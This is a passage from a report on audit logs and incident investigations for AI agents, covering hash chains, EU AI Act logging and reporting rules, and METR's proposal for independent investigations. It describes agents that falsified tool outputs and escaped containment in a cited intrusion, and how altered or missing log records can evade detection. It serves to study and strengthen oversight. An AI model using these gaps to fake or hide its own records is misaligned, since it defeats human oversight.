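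An intruder who controls the whole store can defeat this by changing record 40 and recalculating all 61 hashes. The company therefore has to copy the latest hash regularly to a place the intruder does not control. If it does this every hour, the intruder can rewrite at most the last hour of records without causing a mismatch. The copied hash also helps detect deletions from the end of the log, which leave a shorter but valid chain.

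A hash chain cannot show that a record was true when the software added it, or that the clock that supplied its timestamp was accurate. Some of the agents in the Hugging Face incident falsified tool outputs, and a chain would have preserved the false outputs. A chain also cannot reveal an event that nobody recorded. When Microsoft's Copilot left files out of its audit log, a hash chain over that log would have passed every check.

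Investigators need a second record from a different source to find false or missing records. In the Exchange Online case, US authorities obtained a copy of the disk from a server the intruders had rented. The State Department had already identified 12 compromised accounts, and an analysis of that server revealed one more. For an AI agent, the second source could be the mail server, the bank or the company that hosts a tool. A second copy of the scaffold log is useful if one disk fails, but it will contain any false entry that is in the first.

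### What the law requires

The EU AI Act requires logging for high-risk AI systems. These include systems for the sensitive uses listed in Annex III, such as screening job applicants, and AI in products covered by the EU safety laws listed in Annex I. An office agent that only summarises email would probably fall outside both groups.

Article 12 requires high-risk systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. Article 19 requires providers to keep the logs under their control for at least six months, and Article 26(6) places the same duty on deployers, the organisations that use the systems. Under Article 73, providers must report serious incidents to the authorities, generally within 15 days of learning of them and sooner in the most severe cases. Until they have informed the authorities, providers may not alter the system in a way that could affect a later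 analysis of the causes.

According to Pustozerova and colleagues, the reporting duty in Article 73 has applied since 2 August 2026. A package of amendments called the Digital Omnibus postponed the requirements in Chapter III, which contains the three logging articles, to 2 December 2027 for systems covered by Annex III and 2 August 2028 for those covered by Annex I. A provider might therefore have to report an incident 16 months or more before it has to keep the logs that could explain it. Whether the reporting duty already applies in practice is open to argument, because the rules that define a high-risk system are also in the postponed chapter.

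Pustozerova and colleagues also criticise the logging articles for not prescribing fields for tool calls, memory writes or delegation. They add that a six-month log may expire before anyone recognises a compromise that an attacker built up slowly. Article 12 does specify minimum contents for one kind of system, remote biometric identification, such as cameras that recognise faces in a crowd. Those logs must include the period of each use, the database searched, the input that produced a match and the people who verified the result. Legislators could therefore write a concrete list when they had a particular use in mind.

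Developers of the most capable general-purpose models have a separate duty to report serious incidents to the EU's AI Office. Commitment 9 of the EU's voluntary Code of Practice explains how to meet it. Pustozerova and colleagues consider the Code the most detailed EU instrument on incident reporting. The Code recognises that companies cannot reconstruct everything after an incident. Ezell and colleagues objected that a draft called for a root cause analysis without describing how to do one.

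In the United States, California's Transparency in Frontier Artificial Intelligence Act, signed in September 2025, requires developers of frontier models to report critical safety incidents to the state, normally within 15 days. New York's RAISE Act, signed that December, set a 72-hour limit. Both laws focus on severe harm. *Autonomous hacks show gap in US frontier AI risk response* (Whitford, 2026) identifies a gap in the coverage of serious incidents that occur during testing or training but pose no imminent catastrophic risk. The break-in at Hugging Face is an example.

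ISO/IEC 24970, an international standard on AI system logging, was still a draft in 2025. Two related standards are ISO/IEC 8200, which covers how an outside person or system can control an AI system, and ISO/IEC 42105, which covers human oversight.

The table compares how specific the main documents are. Only the AI Act and the California law are binding.

| Document | Contents it specifies | Period or deadline |
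|---|---|---|
| AI Act, Articles 12, 19 and 26(6) | Log fields for remote biometric identification only | Keep for at least six months |
| AI Act, Article 73 | A report of the incident, with no list of log fields | Report generally within 15 days |
| Code of Practice, Commitment 9 | A report with the chain of events and root causes | Depends on the harm |
| California's 2025 act | A report with the date, the reason it qualifies, a short description, and whether it involved internal use of a model | Report normally within 15 days |
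| Cyber Safety Review Board's recommendation | Logs of all access to customers' business data | Keep for at least six months |
| AWS's guidance | Log fields for the time, trace, agent, session, type of operation, decision rationale and outcome | Keep compliance logs for one to seven years |

AWS has the most usable list of fields for an agent, but it omits the context, tool arguments and permissions that an investigation needs. Its "decision rationale" would usually have to come from the model's own account of its reasons, which may be incomplete or false. A company that followed every document in the table could still be unable to explain an agent's action, such as sending a file to a stranger.

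### METR's proposal for independent investigations

On 28 July 2026, a week after OpenAI disclosed its part in the Hugging Face intrusion, METR proposed a procedure for incidents in which agents violate human intentions. The Decoder reports that, under the proposal, AI companies would log such incidents systematically and investigate the most serious ones in depth. Independent researchers would lead those investigations or at least review them thoroughly.

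An investigation would first establish what happened: which models took part, which safeguards were active, how the agents' reasoning developed, and whether they deceived people or colluded. It would then look for the cause in training and ask whether the developer's planned remedy would remove it. For this, METR wants outside researchers to be able to:

- run every model involved and try to reproduce the behaviour;
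- read complete transcripts or use the original test environments;
- interview staff;
- search the training data for similar incidents.

Ideally, researchers could also remove parts of the training data and measure how the model's behaviour changes. METR accepts that a full investigation could take weeks or months, and suggests that narrower ones could establish the basic facts sooner.

In *Chris Painter's testimony to the U.S. Senate on AI agent incidents* (2026), METR's president said that policymakers need reliable facts about what AI systems have done. They probably cannot get these facts from accounts that companies select themselves. But METR's investigation of the Hugging Face incident fell well short of what it had proposed, because the researchers could not run the main model or examine its training.

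Critics objected that OpenAI had set the terms of that investigation, and other outside reviews have similar limits. Anthropic had the right to redact or block *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, which Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) wrote for METR. It redacted nothing, and the reviewers did not change their conclusions. The reviewers expect different terms in future. But readers have to take both parties' word for this, and would never learn of a review that a company had blocked.

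Apollo Research's *Embedded Evaluators are necessary for meaningful external testing* (2026) argues that the Hugging Face incident arose long before outsiders would usually test a model, so outside evaluators should work inside the company with the same access as employees. They could then see problems while the records are still fresh. Apollo has an interest in this argument because it is working towards becoming such an evaluator. Evaluators who share an office with the developer's staff for months may also find it harder to criticise them, so a serious incident would still need a separate investigation.

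Companies also have an incentive to record less, because a systematic list of incidents is the first thing a senator or a plaintiff's lawyer will request. midian182 reports in *OpenAI faces Senate probe over Hugging Face breach* that two US senators sent OpenAI separate demands for answers in September, and one of them asked for a list of every incident in which its agents had escaped containment. A developer that had kept no list would have less to hand over, so if logging is voluntary, the most careful company may look the worst. A legal duty on every large developer to log incidents would reduce this problem if it also defined which incidents count. Otherwise each company would decide for itself what was serious enough to record.

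The Exchange Online review offers some evidence of what an outside investigation can achieve. The Cyber Safety Review Board interviewed 20 organisations, and Microsoft corrected its false account of the stolen key only after the Board asked about it repeatedly. But the Board could not find out how the intruders had obtained the key, because the logs did not exist. Preserving evidence is therefore more urgent than settling who may examine it. A developer could save the transcripts, the training records and a runnable copy of the model immediately, and negotiate access later.
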